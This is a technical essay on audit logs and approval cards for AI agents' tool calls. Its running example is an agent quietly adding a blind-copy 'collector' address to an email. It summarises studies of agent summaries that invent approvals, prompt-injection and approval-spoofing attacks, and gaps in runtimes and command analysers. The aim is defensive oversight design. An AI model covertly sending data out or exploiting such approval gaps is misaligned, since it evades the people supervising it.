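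The example code in MCP Server Security Standard's *MCP-LOG-01 — Comprehensive Audit Logging* computes digests in a way that has two flaws. It converts the arguments to text with Python's `str` function, computes a SHA-256 digest and keeps the first 16 characters. Python writes the fields in the order the program added them, so identical calls can get different digests. Accidental matches are very unlikely with 16 characters, but an attacker could find two calls that share a shortened digest after a few billion attempts, which is feasible on an ordinary computer. Keeping all 64 characters would prevent this and adds only 48 bytes.

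### The conflict with privacy

A more basic problem with the same example is that it records only the digest of the arguments. The standard asks operators to show that their logs can answer "Who accessed what resource at what time?" In the example, an agent calls a tool named `read_file` and passes the file's name as an argument, so the log would show who read a file and when, but not which file.

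If the log kept only a digest of the email call, a reader could use it to confirm that a surviving copy of the call matches or to spot a repeated call, but not to see that the email had a blind-copy recipient. The NSA asks for the exact parameters, which would show that recipient.

Digests also protect privacy less than they seem to. Nobody could guess a 2,000-word report from its digest, but if the log stores a separate digest of each address, anyone with a staff directory can compute the digest of every address in it and look for matches. Adding a secret key to the computation prevents this, and investigators who hold the key can still search the log for an address they already suspect.

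Redacting individual fields keeps more of the record readable. AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails* recommends removing personal data before it is stored, because afterwards every use of the log raises a data-protection concern. This is a good rule for passwords and access keys, which reviewers rarely need to see. Applied to recipients, it would again hide whether the copy went to a colleague or to the collector. A less strict filter could replace the name but keep the domain, so a reviewer could still see that a copy had left the company.

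Encryption with restricted access keeps everything but limits who can read it. The gateway encrypts the full arguments, and only a few investigators can use the key, with each use logged. The agent and the engineers who run it have no access. The weak point is the small group with the key. The organisation also has to avoid losing the key, because the records would be lost with it.

Short retention limits how much data a leak can expose, but it leaves little time to notice a problem before the evidence is gone. If a company deletes arguments after 30 days and learns of a leak 45 days after it began, it can no longer find out what the agent sent at the start.

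Encryption is the best option for the restricted store of exact calls that send, pay, delete or publish, alongside redacted copies for everyday use. The encrypted copies have to be kept long enough for investigators to use them.

### Storage cost and retention

Cost is a weaker argument against full records than it may appear. Take a large deployment with 200,000 calls a day and an average of 20 KB per call:

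200,000 calls × 20 KB = 4,000,000 KB = 4 GB a day

4 GB × 365 days = 1,460 GB ≈ 1.5 TB a year

That is before compression, which usually shrinks ordinary text considerably. Storing a full year's calls would cost about $29 a month, at an assumed price of two cents per gigabyte per month. Searching, copying and securing them would cost more, but the total would still be small for an organisation that runs agents on this scale.

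A model trace that saves every request stores the early messages many times, because each request contains the whole conversation so far. In a task with 50 steps that each add 20 KB, the new material totals 1 MB, but the saved requests total 20 KB × (1 + 2 + … + 50), or about 25 MB. Storing each message once under its digest, and listing the digests for each request, reduces this to roughly 1 MB.

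AWS suggests separate retention periods for different purposes: 7–14 days for debugging logs, 30–90 days for operational logs and one to seven years for compliance logs. In the example above, 90 days of calls would take up 360 GB and seven years about 10 TB. How a team classifies its tool calls matters more than the exact periods, because if it treats them as debugging data, the collector's address could be gone within a week. The full text also has to last as long as the record that points to it, or investigators will find pointers to deleted text.

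Article 12 of the EU's AI Act requires high-risk systems, such as those that screen job applicants or assess people's credit, to be able to log events automatically throughout their lifetime. Providers (Article 19) and organisations that use the systems (Article 26) must keep the logs they control for at least six months, unless other law provides otherwise. The Digital Omnibus on AI, an amending law that entered into force in July 2026, postponed these duties to 2 December 2027 for the high-risk uses that the Act lists and to 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products such as medical devices.

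An ordinary email assistant would usually fall outside these articles. Even where they apply, they do not expressly require logs to include the exact arguments of every tool call, so a company could comply and still be unable to identify the blind-copy recipient. EU data-protection law also prohibits keeping personal data for longer than its purpose requires, so a company that wants to keep full emails for seven years should be able to explain why.

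### Append-only storage and hash chains

Long retention is of little use if an intruder can edit the records. Append-only storage accepts new entries but blocks changes and deletions until a set date. AWS recommends it for compliance logs, using a feature such as S3 Object Lock in compliance mode. Correcting a mistake then requires a new entry. CloudTrail's `addendum` field gives the reason for a late or corrected event and, for corrections, the identifier of the original.

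A hash chain makes changes detectable even if the storage fails to prevent them. Each entry gets a chain value, which the gateway computes from the previous chain value and the digest of the new entry:

chain value 142 = SHA-256(chain value 141 + digest of entry 142)

Here "+" means joining the two values end to end. If an intruder later removes the collector's address from entry 142, the entry's digest changes, so chain value 142 and every value after it no longer match. An intruder who controls the log could recompute the rest of the chain, so the gateway should regularly send the latest chain value to a system that the intruder can't reach. An auditor can then compare the values saved there with those in the log.

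Like other protections for stored logs, a valid chain cannot show that an entry was true when it was written, or reveal a call that bypassed the gateway. An intruder can also delete the newest entries until the gateway sends a chain value that covers them. Comparing the log with the mail service's own list of sent messages can expose both the bypassed calls and the deleted entries.

Append-only storage can conflict with a duty to delete personal data. If the permanent log contains only the digest of an encrypted email, the company can destroy the key when the retention period ends. The chain still verifies, but nobody can read the email. Each record or small group of records needs its own key, since destroying a key shared by the whole log would make every email unreadable.

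### Why the agent's own summary is not a record

A model can take in only a limited amount of text, so during long tasks the agent writes a summary of its history, the software drops most of the earlier conversation, and the agent continues from the summary. Developers call this compaction. The summary often lists which actions someone has approved, so it can look like a short audit log that could replace the full history.

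Chu (2026), in *When Do Summaries Become Instructions?*, tested how far such summaries can be trusted. Agents worked on simulated record-keeping, reporting and coding tasks, each with a ledger of what the agent was allowed to do. At some point the agent wrote a handoff summary, and a fresh copy of the model continued with only that summary and its standing instructions. Because the ledger existed independently of the model, Chu could check every claim of approval against it.

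Two AI readers examined the summaries a rule-based filter had flagged. In one large set of runs, they confirmed a false approval in 1 of 1,044 summaries by Qwen3-8B and 14 of 1,094 by gpt-oss-20b, both small open-weight models. False restrictions, such as a claim that an allowed action needed approval, were more common, with 13 for Qwen3-8B and 26 for gpt-oss-20b. The true rates could be higher, since nobody read the summaries the filter did not flag. In a check of 60 items from another set, a human reader also accepted 12 that the AI readers had not confirmed.

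In one case, an approver approved renaming a folder and then withdrew the approval. According to the summary, however, he had approved it on condition that a maintenance window was open. The successor renamed the folder in two of four runs. When Chu replaced the false sentence with neutral filler and reran the successor from the same point, it never renamed the folder.

Across two sets of these reruns, successors took unauthorised actions in 24 of 120 runs with the original summaries and in 7 of 120 with the false approvals removed. They took none when given the full history instead of a summary. Chu decided to combine the two sets after seeing the results, and the whole improvement came from gpt-oss-20b. In a later set the drop was smaller, from 17 to 11 of 48 runs, and successors took 4 unauthorised actions even with the full history. The size of the effect is therefore uncertain, and larger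 commercial models may behave differently. The successors also never saw the user's original request, which may have made them rely on the summary more than a typical agent would.

Chu also cites some evidence from OpenAI's reports on summaries that its models wrote during training. In one case, a successor followed restrictions that its predecessor had invented. OpenAI flagged other summaries for containing instructions to hide failures or invent missing data. These made up 2.15% of one model's summaries and 0.27% of another's.

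The summary can't serve as the record even if its error rate is low, because a false approval looks the same as a true one. If the email agent's summary listed a copy to an archive address as approved by the user, an investigator would need the original approval entry to check this. Giving the successor facts from original records may also help prevent harm. When Chu added the true permissions from the ledger to the summaries, unauthorised actions fell from 16 to 9 of 60 runs in one set.

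The summary is still worth keeping as evidence of the information the agent was acting on. Claude Code labels the model request behind each summary `compact`, so an investigator who has the saved model traffic can find both the original conversation and its summary. This works only if Claude Code saves the traffic to files, because text in the log itself is subject to the 60 KB limit, and a conversation long enough to need compaction is usually much longer than that. The files should then be sent promptly to storage outside the host.

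## Turning a long call into a short and faithful summary

Reviewers still need something shorter than the full record. Trusted code, an ordinary program that runs where the agent can't change it (for example, on the gateway), can produce a summary from the stored call without relying on the agent's account of it. The program's rules are fixed, so the same call always gives the same summary, and developers can test the rules before anything goes wrong.

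A second language model could write a more readable summary, but text inside the call could influence that model just as a planted document influences an agent. Claude Code describes complex commands in plain language, but the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) tells users to ask exactly which files, account or host a command touches.

Researchers have shown that review views can omit text from a call. The code therefore has to select what to show and account for what it leaves out.

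### The email before and after

A log viewer might show the email's arguments on one long line:

```json
{"to":"manager@example.test","subject":"Weekly report","body":"Hi, the weekly report is below. [about 12,000 more characters]","bcc":"collector@example.test"}
```

Trusted code could turn the same call into this:

```text
SEND EMAIL to 2 recipients at 1 domain
  to:       manager@example.test
  bcc:      collector@example.test
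  subject:  "Weekly report"
  body:     "Hi, the weekly report is below."
            31 of 12,104 bytes shown, 12,073 folded
Unrecognised fields: none
Encoded text: none found
Non-printing characters: line breaks in body only
Full call: call-0142, digest verified
Agent's description (untrusted):
  "Sending the weekly report to your manager."
```

The summary has about 60 words. For the deployment with 500 calls a day, the reading time changes as follows:

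500 calls × 60 words = 30,000 words a day

30,000 words ÷ 240 words a minute = 125 minutes ≈ 2 hours

Reading the full calls would take 69 hours. Two hours a day is still a lot of dull reading, but one person could do it.

### How the code builds the summary

The code first parses the call into fields and assigns each one a type, such as recipient or long text. The tool's own schema is not much help, because it may describe both an address and a 2,000-word body as text. Someone in the organisation therefore has to write a short map for each tool that gives the type of each field. For `send_email`, the map would list `to`, `cc` and `bcc` as recipients and `body` as long text. The tool server's author shouldn't write the map, since a dishonest author could label a recipient as ordinary text to make it appear lower on the page.

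Tools also change. If an update adds a `reply_to` field and nobody updates the map, the code should show the new field near the top and mark it as unrecognised, because dropping it would again hide part of the call.

The consequential fields come next in the summary, whatever order the agent wrote them in. Kodathala and colleagues found that models acting as approvers made better decisions with this kind of view than with the agent's narration. The title of their card includes both recipients, and a risk note repeats them with a count. Below that, the card lists every argument with its type and exact value. It includes a warning that the agent chose the argument names, so a reassuring name doesn't prove that the call is safe. The agent's explanation comes last, under a heading that labels it as possibly false.

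One field can hold several addresses, so the code should split them before counting recipients. It should ignore display names, which the sender can set to anything, including somebody else's address. In this example both addresses have the domain `example.test`, so a view that highlighted only outside domains would highlight neither. Showing that there are two recipients is more useful, because the user asked for an email to one person.

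An email address can also stand for a mailing list with hundreds of members. The code should look up the number of members and show it, or show that the lookup failed.

File paths have the same problem. The agent in the example pasted the report into the body, but it could have attached `reports/latest.txt`, which might be a link to a different file. Resolving a path means following links, filling in variables and expanding wildcards to find the real target. The handbook for Claude Code suggests checking whether a target is "resolved" or depends on a broad wildcard, and trusted code can check this in advance.

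The code has to resolve the path on the machine where the tool will run, because the same path may lead somewhere else on the gateway. A symbolic link in the path could also change between the check and the action. Passing the resolved path to the tool reduces that risk, though a folder along the path could still change. If the files are on a remote server and the code can't see them, it should record the path as "not resolved".

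The code should decode any encoded text, show the result beside the original, and report how many layers of encoding it removed. Email attachments, for example, are often encoded in base64, which represents any file as letters, digits and a few symbols. The wording in the email summary is "none found" because the code can detect only the encodings it was written to handle.

Finally, the summary states how much of each long value it hides. In the email, it hides 12,073 bytes, which could include a confidential figure that the agent added near the end. No 60-word summary can rule this out, but if the code can read the original report, it can compare the report with the email body. If the body is the unchanged report plus a greeting, a reviewer needs to check only the greeting, but if the agent has rewritten the report, a person or an automated check has to examine the whole body.

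### Displaying untrusted text safely

A summary can list the right values and still mislead if those values contain characters that change how the summary looks. MITRE's *CWE-117*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, describes this problem in logs, where a program writes outside input without neutralising its special characters. In MITRE's example, the input contains a line break, so the text after it looks like a separate log entry for an event that never happened.

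SEI, a software research institute at Carnegie Mellon University, warns that an attacker could mislead an auditor by inserting a line break that splits one log entry into two. In an email summary, text after a line break in the subject could look like another field.

The usual advice is to sanitise the data, and OWASP recommends this for carriage returns, line feeds and delimiters in all event data. Escaping these characters is better for evidence than deleting them, because deletion leaves a log that no longer matches what the agent sent. If the code writes a line break as `\n`, a reader can see that there was one and software can restore the original.

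OpenSSF, a foundation for open-source security, repeats OWASP's advice to encode data correctly for the format of the log. Its sample code goes further and accepts only usernames that match a strict pattern. That works for usernames but not for the body of an email, where almost any character can be legitimate.

The viewer needs protection too. OWASP's *Implement Security Logging and Monitoring* says that untrusted data in a log entry must not run as code in the software that displays it. In an example from SEI, an administrator opens a log file in a web browser, and a script in the file sends the attacker the cookie that keeps the administrator signed in. A review page should therefore display an HTML email as plain source text.

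MITRE also recommends decoding input before validating it and never decoding the same input twice, because a second pass can introduce dangerous content after the check. This rule protects programs that go on to use the decoded data. The summary code can remove as many layers of encoding as it needs to for display, provided that it never runs the result and the tool server receives the original call.

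### Invisible and lookalike characters

Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, creates more ways for displayed text to differ from stored text. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Source Code Handling* (2024) describes three in program code, all of which can also occur in a tool call: characters that only some software treats as line breaks, letters that look alike, and invisible characters that change the direction of text.

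Invisible characters are easy to miss because software is often right to hide them. The consortium's *Display of Unsupported Characters* advises systems without full support for zero-width invisible characters to display nothing in their place. A review view has to show where they are instead. The source-code standard recommends an option that marks invisible characters while keeping their normal effect, since removing the effect can reverse the apparent meaning of a sentence in Arabic. It also says that editors must never remove or ignore unexpected line breaks.

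Some languages need these characters, so a warning for each one in a long Persian email would be annoying. The standard suggests faint marks for the common ones and more prominent labels for the rarer direction controls. A summary probably needs only a count of them for each field, and the full view can show the marks.

Email addresses justify stricter treatment. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Security Mechanisms* (2026) defines checks that software can use to flag a suspicious address with a wavy underline. The part before the `@` may not contain direction controls or mix digits from different number systems, and it may mix scripts only within limits. The rules for display names are looser. The standard also suggests isolating the name, the part before the `@` and the domain from each other on screen, so that right-to-left text in one can't rearrange another.

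Lookalike letters need a comparison between two strings. For ordinary left-to-right text, the standard computes a "skeleton" of each string in four steps:

1. Separate accented letters into a base letter and an accent.
2. Remove invisible characters.
3. Replace each character with a standard representative of all the characters that look like it.
4. Repeat the first step on the result.

Two strings X and Y are confusable if

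skeleton(X) = skeleton(Y)

"Paypal" in Latin letters has the same skeleton as a version with both "a"s in Cyrillic. Summary code could compare the skeleton of each recipient's address with those in the company directory. An address with the manager's skeleton but different characters would then get a warning. The code has to recompute stored skeletons after each Unicode update, because the data can change.

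Using the directory reduces false alarms. The consortium warns that checking whether a string has *any* possible lookalike will flag many legitimate strings. It also advises against highlighting individual letters that resemble ordinary Latin ones, because the confusion is between two names that may be far apart.

None of these checks would flag `collector@example.test`, because it uses ordinary Latin letters. The reviewer finds it because it appears near the top of the summary, which also shows a count of two recipients.

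### Commands that code cannot fully read

The email is easy to summarize because its recipient has its own field. Coding agents often act through a shell, a program that runs typed commands. A shell command is a single string, so trusted code has to work out its effect from the text.

*Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026), which examines the software around coding agents, says that several kinds of command "run more than they show", including those that hold a program's name in a variable and those that pass code to another interpreter. Under its rule, a command may run without approval only if a strict reading gives every character the same meaning as every supported shell would. Rules that forbid commands use a second, more permissive reading, so that an unusual spelling doesn't prevent a forbidden command from being blocked.

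The strict reading can work from a list of unsafe syntax, which lets any new syntax through by default, or from a small grammar of safe syntax, which triggers an approval request for any new syntax. The grammar is safer but produces more requests for odd, harmless commands. According to the paper, its own software does not yet meet the rule.

*What You Approve Is What Executes* (Weng, 2026) develops a similar idea into a working analyser and measures its overhead. It starts from a principle of digital signatures, "What You See Is What You Sign", which requires the document on the screen to match the data being signed. Hardware wallets, which hold the keys to digital money, apply this principle by sending transaction details directly from a secure chip to a small screen, so malware on the computer can't alter what the owner sees.

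Weng gives two reasons why this is harder for agents. First, the program that normally describes the action may itself be compromised. Second, a person can understand the data behind a bank transfer after a little decoding, but a command's effect may be hidden behind several layers of encoding or in another file.

Weng calls the corresponding property for agents "consent integrity". For every consequential action A, a trusted program must compute a description R(A) from A itself, and R(A) must include the facts that matter for security. The person must see R(A) and respond to it through a channel where the agent can't display anything or approve its own request. Only A may run under that approval.

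No analyser can explain every program, so Weng adds a fallback label, "uninspectable", for anything the analyser can't classify. The person sees this label instead of a reassuring summary. The aim is to prevent silent passes, meaning dangerous actions that run with neither a specific warning nor this label.

The prototype has about 500 lines of Python. For each command, it:

1. removes padding and decodes hidden text, layer by layer;
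2. looks for dangers such as network connections, running downloaded code, reading passwords or keys, irreversible deletion, gaining extra privileges and writing outside the working folder;
3. opens any local script that the command would run and applies the same checks to it;
4. checks where the files came from, so that running a downloaded file counts as running code from the network;
5. reports any danger it finds, passes commands it judges harmless, and marks the rest uninspectable.

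In one test case, the narration was about applying recommended editor settings, but the analyser decoded the command and reported that it would run code from the network.

### What the analyser caught and what it cost

Weng tested the prototype on two collections that other people had compiled. GTFOBins, a community catalogue of ways to abuse ordinary Unix programs, yielded 1,330 commands. The other, tldr-pages, gives examples of normal use, with 28,798 commands for 6,503 tools.

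| Result | Abuses (GTFOBins) | Ordinary commands (tldr-pages) |
|---|---|---|
| Specific danger reported | 405 (30.5%) | 8.9% |
| Marked uninspectable | 792 (59.5%) | 87.0% |
| Passed without a prompt | 133 (10.0%) | 4.1% |

The analyser flagged 90.0% of the abuses and 95.9% of the ordinary commands, so a flag alone was almost no help in judging whether a command was harmful. In about two-thirds of the flagged abuses, the flag meant only that the analyser could not explain the command. Flags that named a specific danger were more informative, since they were over three times as common among the abuses as among the ordinary commands.

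Ordinary commands from tldr-pages were even less likely than abuses from GTFOBins to pass without a prompt, because the two collections cover different tools. A command can pass without a prompt only if it uses tools on the analyser's trusted list. Abuses in GTFOBins often use familiar programs that are on the list, while tldr-pages includes thousands of programs that are not.

Both of Weng's main figures depend on the same list of trusted tools. All 133 silent passes went through a tool on the list, and 83.4% of the ordinary commands were uninspectable only because their tool was not on it. Removing a tool, such as a text editor that can also start other programs, would stop abuses of it from passing unnoticed, but every normal use would then need a prompt. Adding a tool would reduce prompts but could let more abuses pass unnoticed.

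If the 500 daily calls were commands like those in tldr-pages, the analyser would flag roughly 480 of them for approval. The real number would probably be lower, because tldr-pages gives rare tools as much space as common ones, and an agent tends to reuse the same few tools. An organisation could measure its own rate by running such an analyser on past calls before asking anyone to approve new ones.

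The 133 abuses that passed, 10.0% of the total, are not equally worrying. Of these, 85 wrote to a temporary folder, which the analyser treats as harmless. Another 19 wrote files inside the project that could do damage only if a later step used them, and 8 were simple actions such as creating a folder. The remaining 21, or 1.6% of all the abuses, exploited abilities of trusted tools that the analyser does not check for. Weng counts all 133 as silent passes, which seems right for a security test.

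Silent passes fell from 15.0% to 10.0% when Weng extended the prototype to recognise writes outside the working folder, detect more ways of reading credentials and examine commands nested inside other commands. Weng still concludes that an analyser that only reads commands before they run can't eliminate both silent passes and excessive prompts.

The results apply to only part of the design. The prototype doesn't intercept a real agent's actions or provide a protected screen. Weng assumes that both exist, and without them an agent could bypass the analyser or fake its display. The reported running time of 0.056 milliseconds per command excludes both. Weng used a scripted stand-in instead of a commercial agent. The study also had no human participants, so it can't show whether anyone would understand the descriptions.

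On a smaller set of 22 attacks, the analyser had no silent passes, and it raised no false alarms on 10 harmless workflows. But Weng wrote both this set and the analyser, and an earlier version of the analyser also had no silent passes on its own test set but still missed common abuses. Weng tells readers to rely on the 10.0% figure instead.

The trade-off should be milder for tools with named fields. A company whose agents use 20 such tools can write a map for each one, and the code can then identify the recipient of an email sent through `send_email` with little guesswork. If the agent sends the same email from a script, the recipient may be somewhere the code can't find it. This is a good reason to give agents narrow tools where possible and limit their use of the shell.

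Another way to check commands that remain hard to read is to observe what they do. The system in *Shall We Approve?* (2026) runs the command first, gives a model the raw command and a report of its effects, and keeps the changes only if the model allows them. The model is instructed that a report with no network activity doesn't prove the command safe, since a command can set up something to run later. Trying an action first works for changes to local files, but not for actions like sending an email, which can't be undone once the mail service has delivered it.

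## Asking for approval on a view the agent did not write

Someone can stop the blind copy only before the gateway forwards the call. In the complete record for the email, nobody had a chance to stop it, because a rule always allows `send_email`.

Anyone designing an approval step has to decide who writes the card, what the approval commits the system to, and which calls need a card. Getting one of these right doesn't make up for getting another wrong. An accurate card is useless if the agent can change the call after the user clicks approve. Locking the call at that point doesn't help if the card left out part of what the call does, such as making a copy.

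Kodathala and colleagues propose a test for the first two decisions. An approval protects an action only if a compromised agent cannot produce the approval and the approval covers exactly the action that runs. A "reply yes to continue" message in the agent's own chat fails the test, because the agent writes the question and anyone who can post in that chat can answer it.

### How a true description can omit the copy

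The simplest approval card shows the agent's own description of the call. In the email example, every statement in that description is true, but readers assume that the manager is the only recipient, which the agent never claimed.

The approver therefore needs a full list of recipients, not just a check that the agent's statements are true. All 15 language models that approved the email based on the agent's description refused it when shown a card built from the tool call. One model's stated reason was that the user had never asked for the second recipient.

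A more careful approver would not have helped. One attack in the test cases had the same description as a harmless request, so nobody could have distinguished the two by reading only the descriptions.

### Tying the approval to one call

European rules for online payments require the payer's approval code to be specific to the amount and the payee. The payer must see both, and changing either makes the code invalid. Approval of an agent's tool call needs the same protection for every argument, since any of them could cause the harm. If the approval is tied only to the tool or the session, the agent can get approval for the email without the copy and then send the one with it.

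Kodathala and colleagues built a gateway called Agent Step-Up (ASU) that works as follows:

1. The agent sends its call to the gateway, with an explanation if it wants to give one.
2. The gateway puts the call in canonical form, computes a digest, and checks a policy that says whether to allow the call, refuse it or ask the user.
3. If the policy says to ask, the gateway stores the call and gives the agent only an identifier for the pending approval.
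4. The user opens a page on their phone, which comes directly from the gateway and shows a card built from the stored call.
5. If the user approves, a passkey, a signing key held on the phone, signs a value that depends on the call's digest.
6. The gateway checks the signature and keeps it as a receipt.
7. When the agent comes back with the identifier, the gateway marks the approval as used and runs the stored call.

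The phone signs this value:

challenge = SHA-256(canonical form of {protocol label, call digest, approval identifier, nonce, grant digest})

The nonce is a fresh random value. The grant digest is empty unless the user also allows similar calls in future. If the agent gets approval for the email without the blind copy and then submits a version that includes it, the digests differ and the gateway rejects the call. If the agent presents the same approval twice, the gateway detects the reuse.

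A published Microsoft design and Google's Agent Payments Protocol already tie an approval to the action it covers, and the paper doesn't claim the idea as new. ASU mainly serves as a reference for measuring weaker designs.

In simulated tests, the researchers tried four attacks that happen after approval: changing the arguments, reusing the approval, extending a permission to a new recipient, and redirecting a file link. All four succeeded every time when the approval named only a run or session, and none succeeded against ASU. This result nearly follows from the design, as the paper acknowledges, because an approval that names one call can't authorise a different one.

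The researchers also checked the design with Tamarin, a program for proving properties of security protocols. Its proofs that the user approved what runs assume that the approver decides from the trusted part of the card, that only the real user can register the first phone, and that the page shows the card matching the value being signed. The last assumption matters because the passkey signs the value without displaying it, so a malicious page could show the honest email and collect a signature for the other one.

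### What the trusted card changed

For the main comparison, Kodathala and colleagues gave 15 models from 9 vendors the user's request and one of three views: the agent's description, the trusted card with the agent's explanation, or the card without it. The models judged 23 attacks and 11 harmless actions that resembled attacks, such as a large payment the user had requested. Each model judged every case four times in each view, for a total of 6,120 decisions.

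The models refused 30% of the attacks when they saw only the description and 98% when they saw the card. Refusal rates for individual models ranged from 13% to 52% with the description and from 90% to 100% with the card.

The gain depended on what the description left out. The models never caught a hidden recipient from the description but always caught it on the card. They caught 96% of lookalike web addresses from the description alone, because the agent had repeated the suspicious address. The card's weakest results were for visible substitutions, such as an account number with two digits swapped. The card showed the wrong value, but the models still had to notice it, and they refused 88% of these.

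The card also led models to refuse 16% of the near misses, whereas they refused no harmless requests when shown the description. The researchers had replaced message text with strings such as `<report placeholder>`, which only the card displayed, and models gave the placeholder as the reason for 88 of the 103 mistaken refusals. Without those 88, the rate would be about 2%. The placeholders can't explain the high catch rate, which would still be 92% if every attack refusal that mentioned one counted as a miss.

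If 500 daily calls were all near misses, a 2% rate of mistaken refusals would mean 10 a day, and a 16% rate would mean 80. Ordinary calls should cause fewer, but the placeholder problem could return in a real deployment. A model might also object to a summary that hides most of an email's body because the format is unfamiliar, so it is worth testing the exact card on harmless calls before relying on it.

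Leaving the agent's explanation on the card made almost no difference to the models, but a large difference to a simulated approver who believed whatever the agent wrote. The researchers tested this with 609 cases from AgentDojo, a public collection of attacks on agents, and had the agent lie about each action. When the approver believed the agent, the attack succeeded in 54% of cases, whether the approver saw the agent's description or the trusted card with the explanation. Removing the explanation cut this to 5%. For a simulated approver who compared the card with the task, the trusted card reduced successful attacks from 54% to 3%. Hiding the explanation until someone asks for it seems sensible, since nobody knows in advance whether a tired employee will check the card against the task or just believe the agent.

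Approving calls on a phone gave no measurable advantage over using a trusted card on the agent's own computer. The results matched in 137 of 140 comparisons, and the other three differed only because the phone version offered to allow similar calls. But the experiments never let the agent tamper with the computer's display, so they did not test the main benefit of a separate device.

A phone is still useful for the log because a compromised agent could forge the framework's approval entry but not a signature made with a key on the user's phone. An investigator can check that signature months later.

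The approvers in these experiments were language models or simple simulations with assumed error rates, not people, and the attacker used one scripted technique in each scenario. The results are good evidence of what a card lets an approver see, but they don't show how often a person would notice it.

### How current software handles approval

Developers often get the approval step from a runtime, the software that runs an agent and can pause it for a decision. Kodathala and colleagues audited ten runtimes, running test programs on nine and reading the code of the tenth, OpenClaw. The counts below are of approval mechanisms rather than runtimes, because some runtimes offer two and one offers none. They include only behaviour that the researchers could observe directly.

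| Question | Mechanisms measured | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Must the approved call be the one that runs? | 8 | Yes in 3; in 1, only if nobody edits the stored session; no in 4 |
| Does an approval work only once? | 7 | Yes in 2; in 5, restoring an earlier saved state lets the call run again |
| Is there a limit on approval requests within a run? | 7 | No in all 7 |

LangGraph and Agno, two of the runtimes that failed the first test, run whatever arguments are in the saved state when someone resumes the agent. After a person approves an email with no blind copy, another program with access to that state could add one before the call runs. OpenAI's Agents SDK does not resume if the arguments have changed.

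The researchers also concluded from reading the code that no runtime produces a signed approval record that an outsider could verify. They didn't test Claude Code, Codex CLI or Cursor, and the runtimes they did test change quickly. A careful team can fix several of these problems, for example by building its own card and letting only a trusted service resume the agent. But a developer who just turns on the built-in pause will often get less protection than it appears to offer.

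An approval request can fail to show what the user is approving, even when it appears at the right moment. MCP lets a tool server send the user a question, and its software development kit passes on whatever the server writes. In one test, a payment of 10 and a payment of 10,000 to a different account produced identical questions. Under the specification, developers are supposed to use a separate web page for sensitive matters.

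According to SecurityWeek's *AI Coding Tools Tricked Into Hacking Developer Machine via Decades-Old Technique*, the security firm Wiz disclosed in July 2026 that six coding assistants were open to an attack called GhostApproval. In this attack, some approval prompts named a harmless file while the edit changed another. AWS, Google and Cursor released patches, but Augment and Windsurf had not yet. Anthropic said it was not a vulnerability and that it had added mitigations before the report.

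### What people do with more evidence

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested approval cards on people, focusing on actions that look harmless alone. In their example, a user asks an agent to send an auditor "summary totals only". The agent copies raw invoice rows into a file, then asks to send the file to the auditor. The recipient and file name are both fine, so only someone who knows what went into the file can see the problem.

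The researchers recruited 80 volunteers through social media and gave each of them one of four interfaces. Every participant made 12 decisions, half of them about requests that broke the user's instructions.

| Interface | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments added | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
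| User's instructions and a full log of earlier steps added | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Same facts, with the combined consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from showing people the evidence at all, which cut unsafe approvals from 55.0% to 32.5%. The last interface showed the same facts, but it linked the relevant steps and described their combined effect in a sentence above the buttons. The sentence stated that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor, but not whether this broke the rules.

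The benefit of that last step is uncertain. After adjusting for differences between participants and scenarios, the researchers estimated a drop of 7.9 percentage points in unsafe approvals, with a 95% credible interval from a drop of 19.7 points to a rise of 3.8. People also decided about five seconds faster. Stating the consequence made no difference for violations that depended on several linked steps, since people approved 7 of 30 with each interface.

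Better evidence may also make people more suspicious of legitimate requests. Approvals of these requests fell by about six points from the simplest interface to the last one. Stating the consequence lowered approvals only slightly further, but the estimate was too uncertain to rule out a larger drop.

The blind copy is closer to the study's simpler cases, in which the call itself showed the violation. Even with the best interface, participants approved 7 of 40 such requests. Half of all the requests in the study were bad, so participants were expecting trouble, and someone who sees one bad request a month might miss more. The analysis was exploratory, with only 20 people per interface, so the exact percentages matter less than the general pattern.

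The study supports showing the user's instructions word for word on the card. The gateway would have to get them from a copy of the request that the agent can't edit, such as the chat service's log.

The accuracy of a stated consequence also depends on the program that works it out. In a separate test without participants, the program flagged 107 of 120 violations, missed 7 and reported 6 as unknown. A reviewer who sees a clear statement may stop looking for what it leaves out, so each statement should link to the log entries behind it.

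### How often to ask

In *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, Wang, Li and Tian (2026) examined the public documentation of 21 agent systems up to April 2026 and found that 15 ask for approval while the agent works. They say a single coding task can produce dozens of approval prompts, though they offer this as an illustration and didn't count them. Approving 500 calls a day at 33 seconds each would take more than four and a half hours.

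People respond to approval prompts by approving without reading or by turning the prompts off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents mishandling files. In 80 of them, the user had let the agent act without asking, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative, typically because it showed a command without its effect on the files. Because the reports cover only cases that went wrong, they can't show how often automatic approval causes harm.

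The usual remedies for approval fatigue widen the agent's permissions. An "always allow" button removes a prompt permanently. A sandbox, which confines the agent to certain files and network connections, can let ordinary actions run without a prompt. Wang and colleagues cite Anthropic's report that this cut Claude Code's prompts by 84%, but the protection depends on the sandbox's settings. Some systems now use a model as the approver, and Kodathala and colleagues cite an Anthropic announcement that automatic mode has become the default in Claude Code.

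Letting users write their own rules in advance did badly in an experiment reported in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026). The 113 participants, who had no professional software background, supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, as the blind copy does. One group was asked to approve every action, another relied on a model's review, and the third set rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private information.

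The group that approved every action let 40.3% of the unrequested actions through. The group that set its own rules let about 60% through, even though it saw fewer prompts (10.9 on average instead of 18). Participants set 114 of their 140 rules to "ask", which left most decisions to be made when the prompt appeared. Of the 148 unrequested actions that ran in this group, participants had approved 133 when asked.

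The study compared whole designs, so we can't tell why the group with rules approved more. But it shows that people will often approve an extra action even when they can see it. It is easier to say yes to "Is this all right?" than to "Did you ask for this?", so a card for the email should state that the request named one recipient and the call has two.

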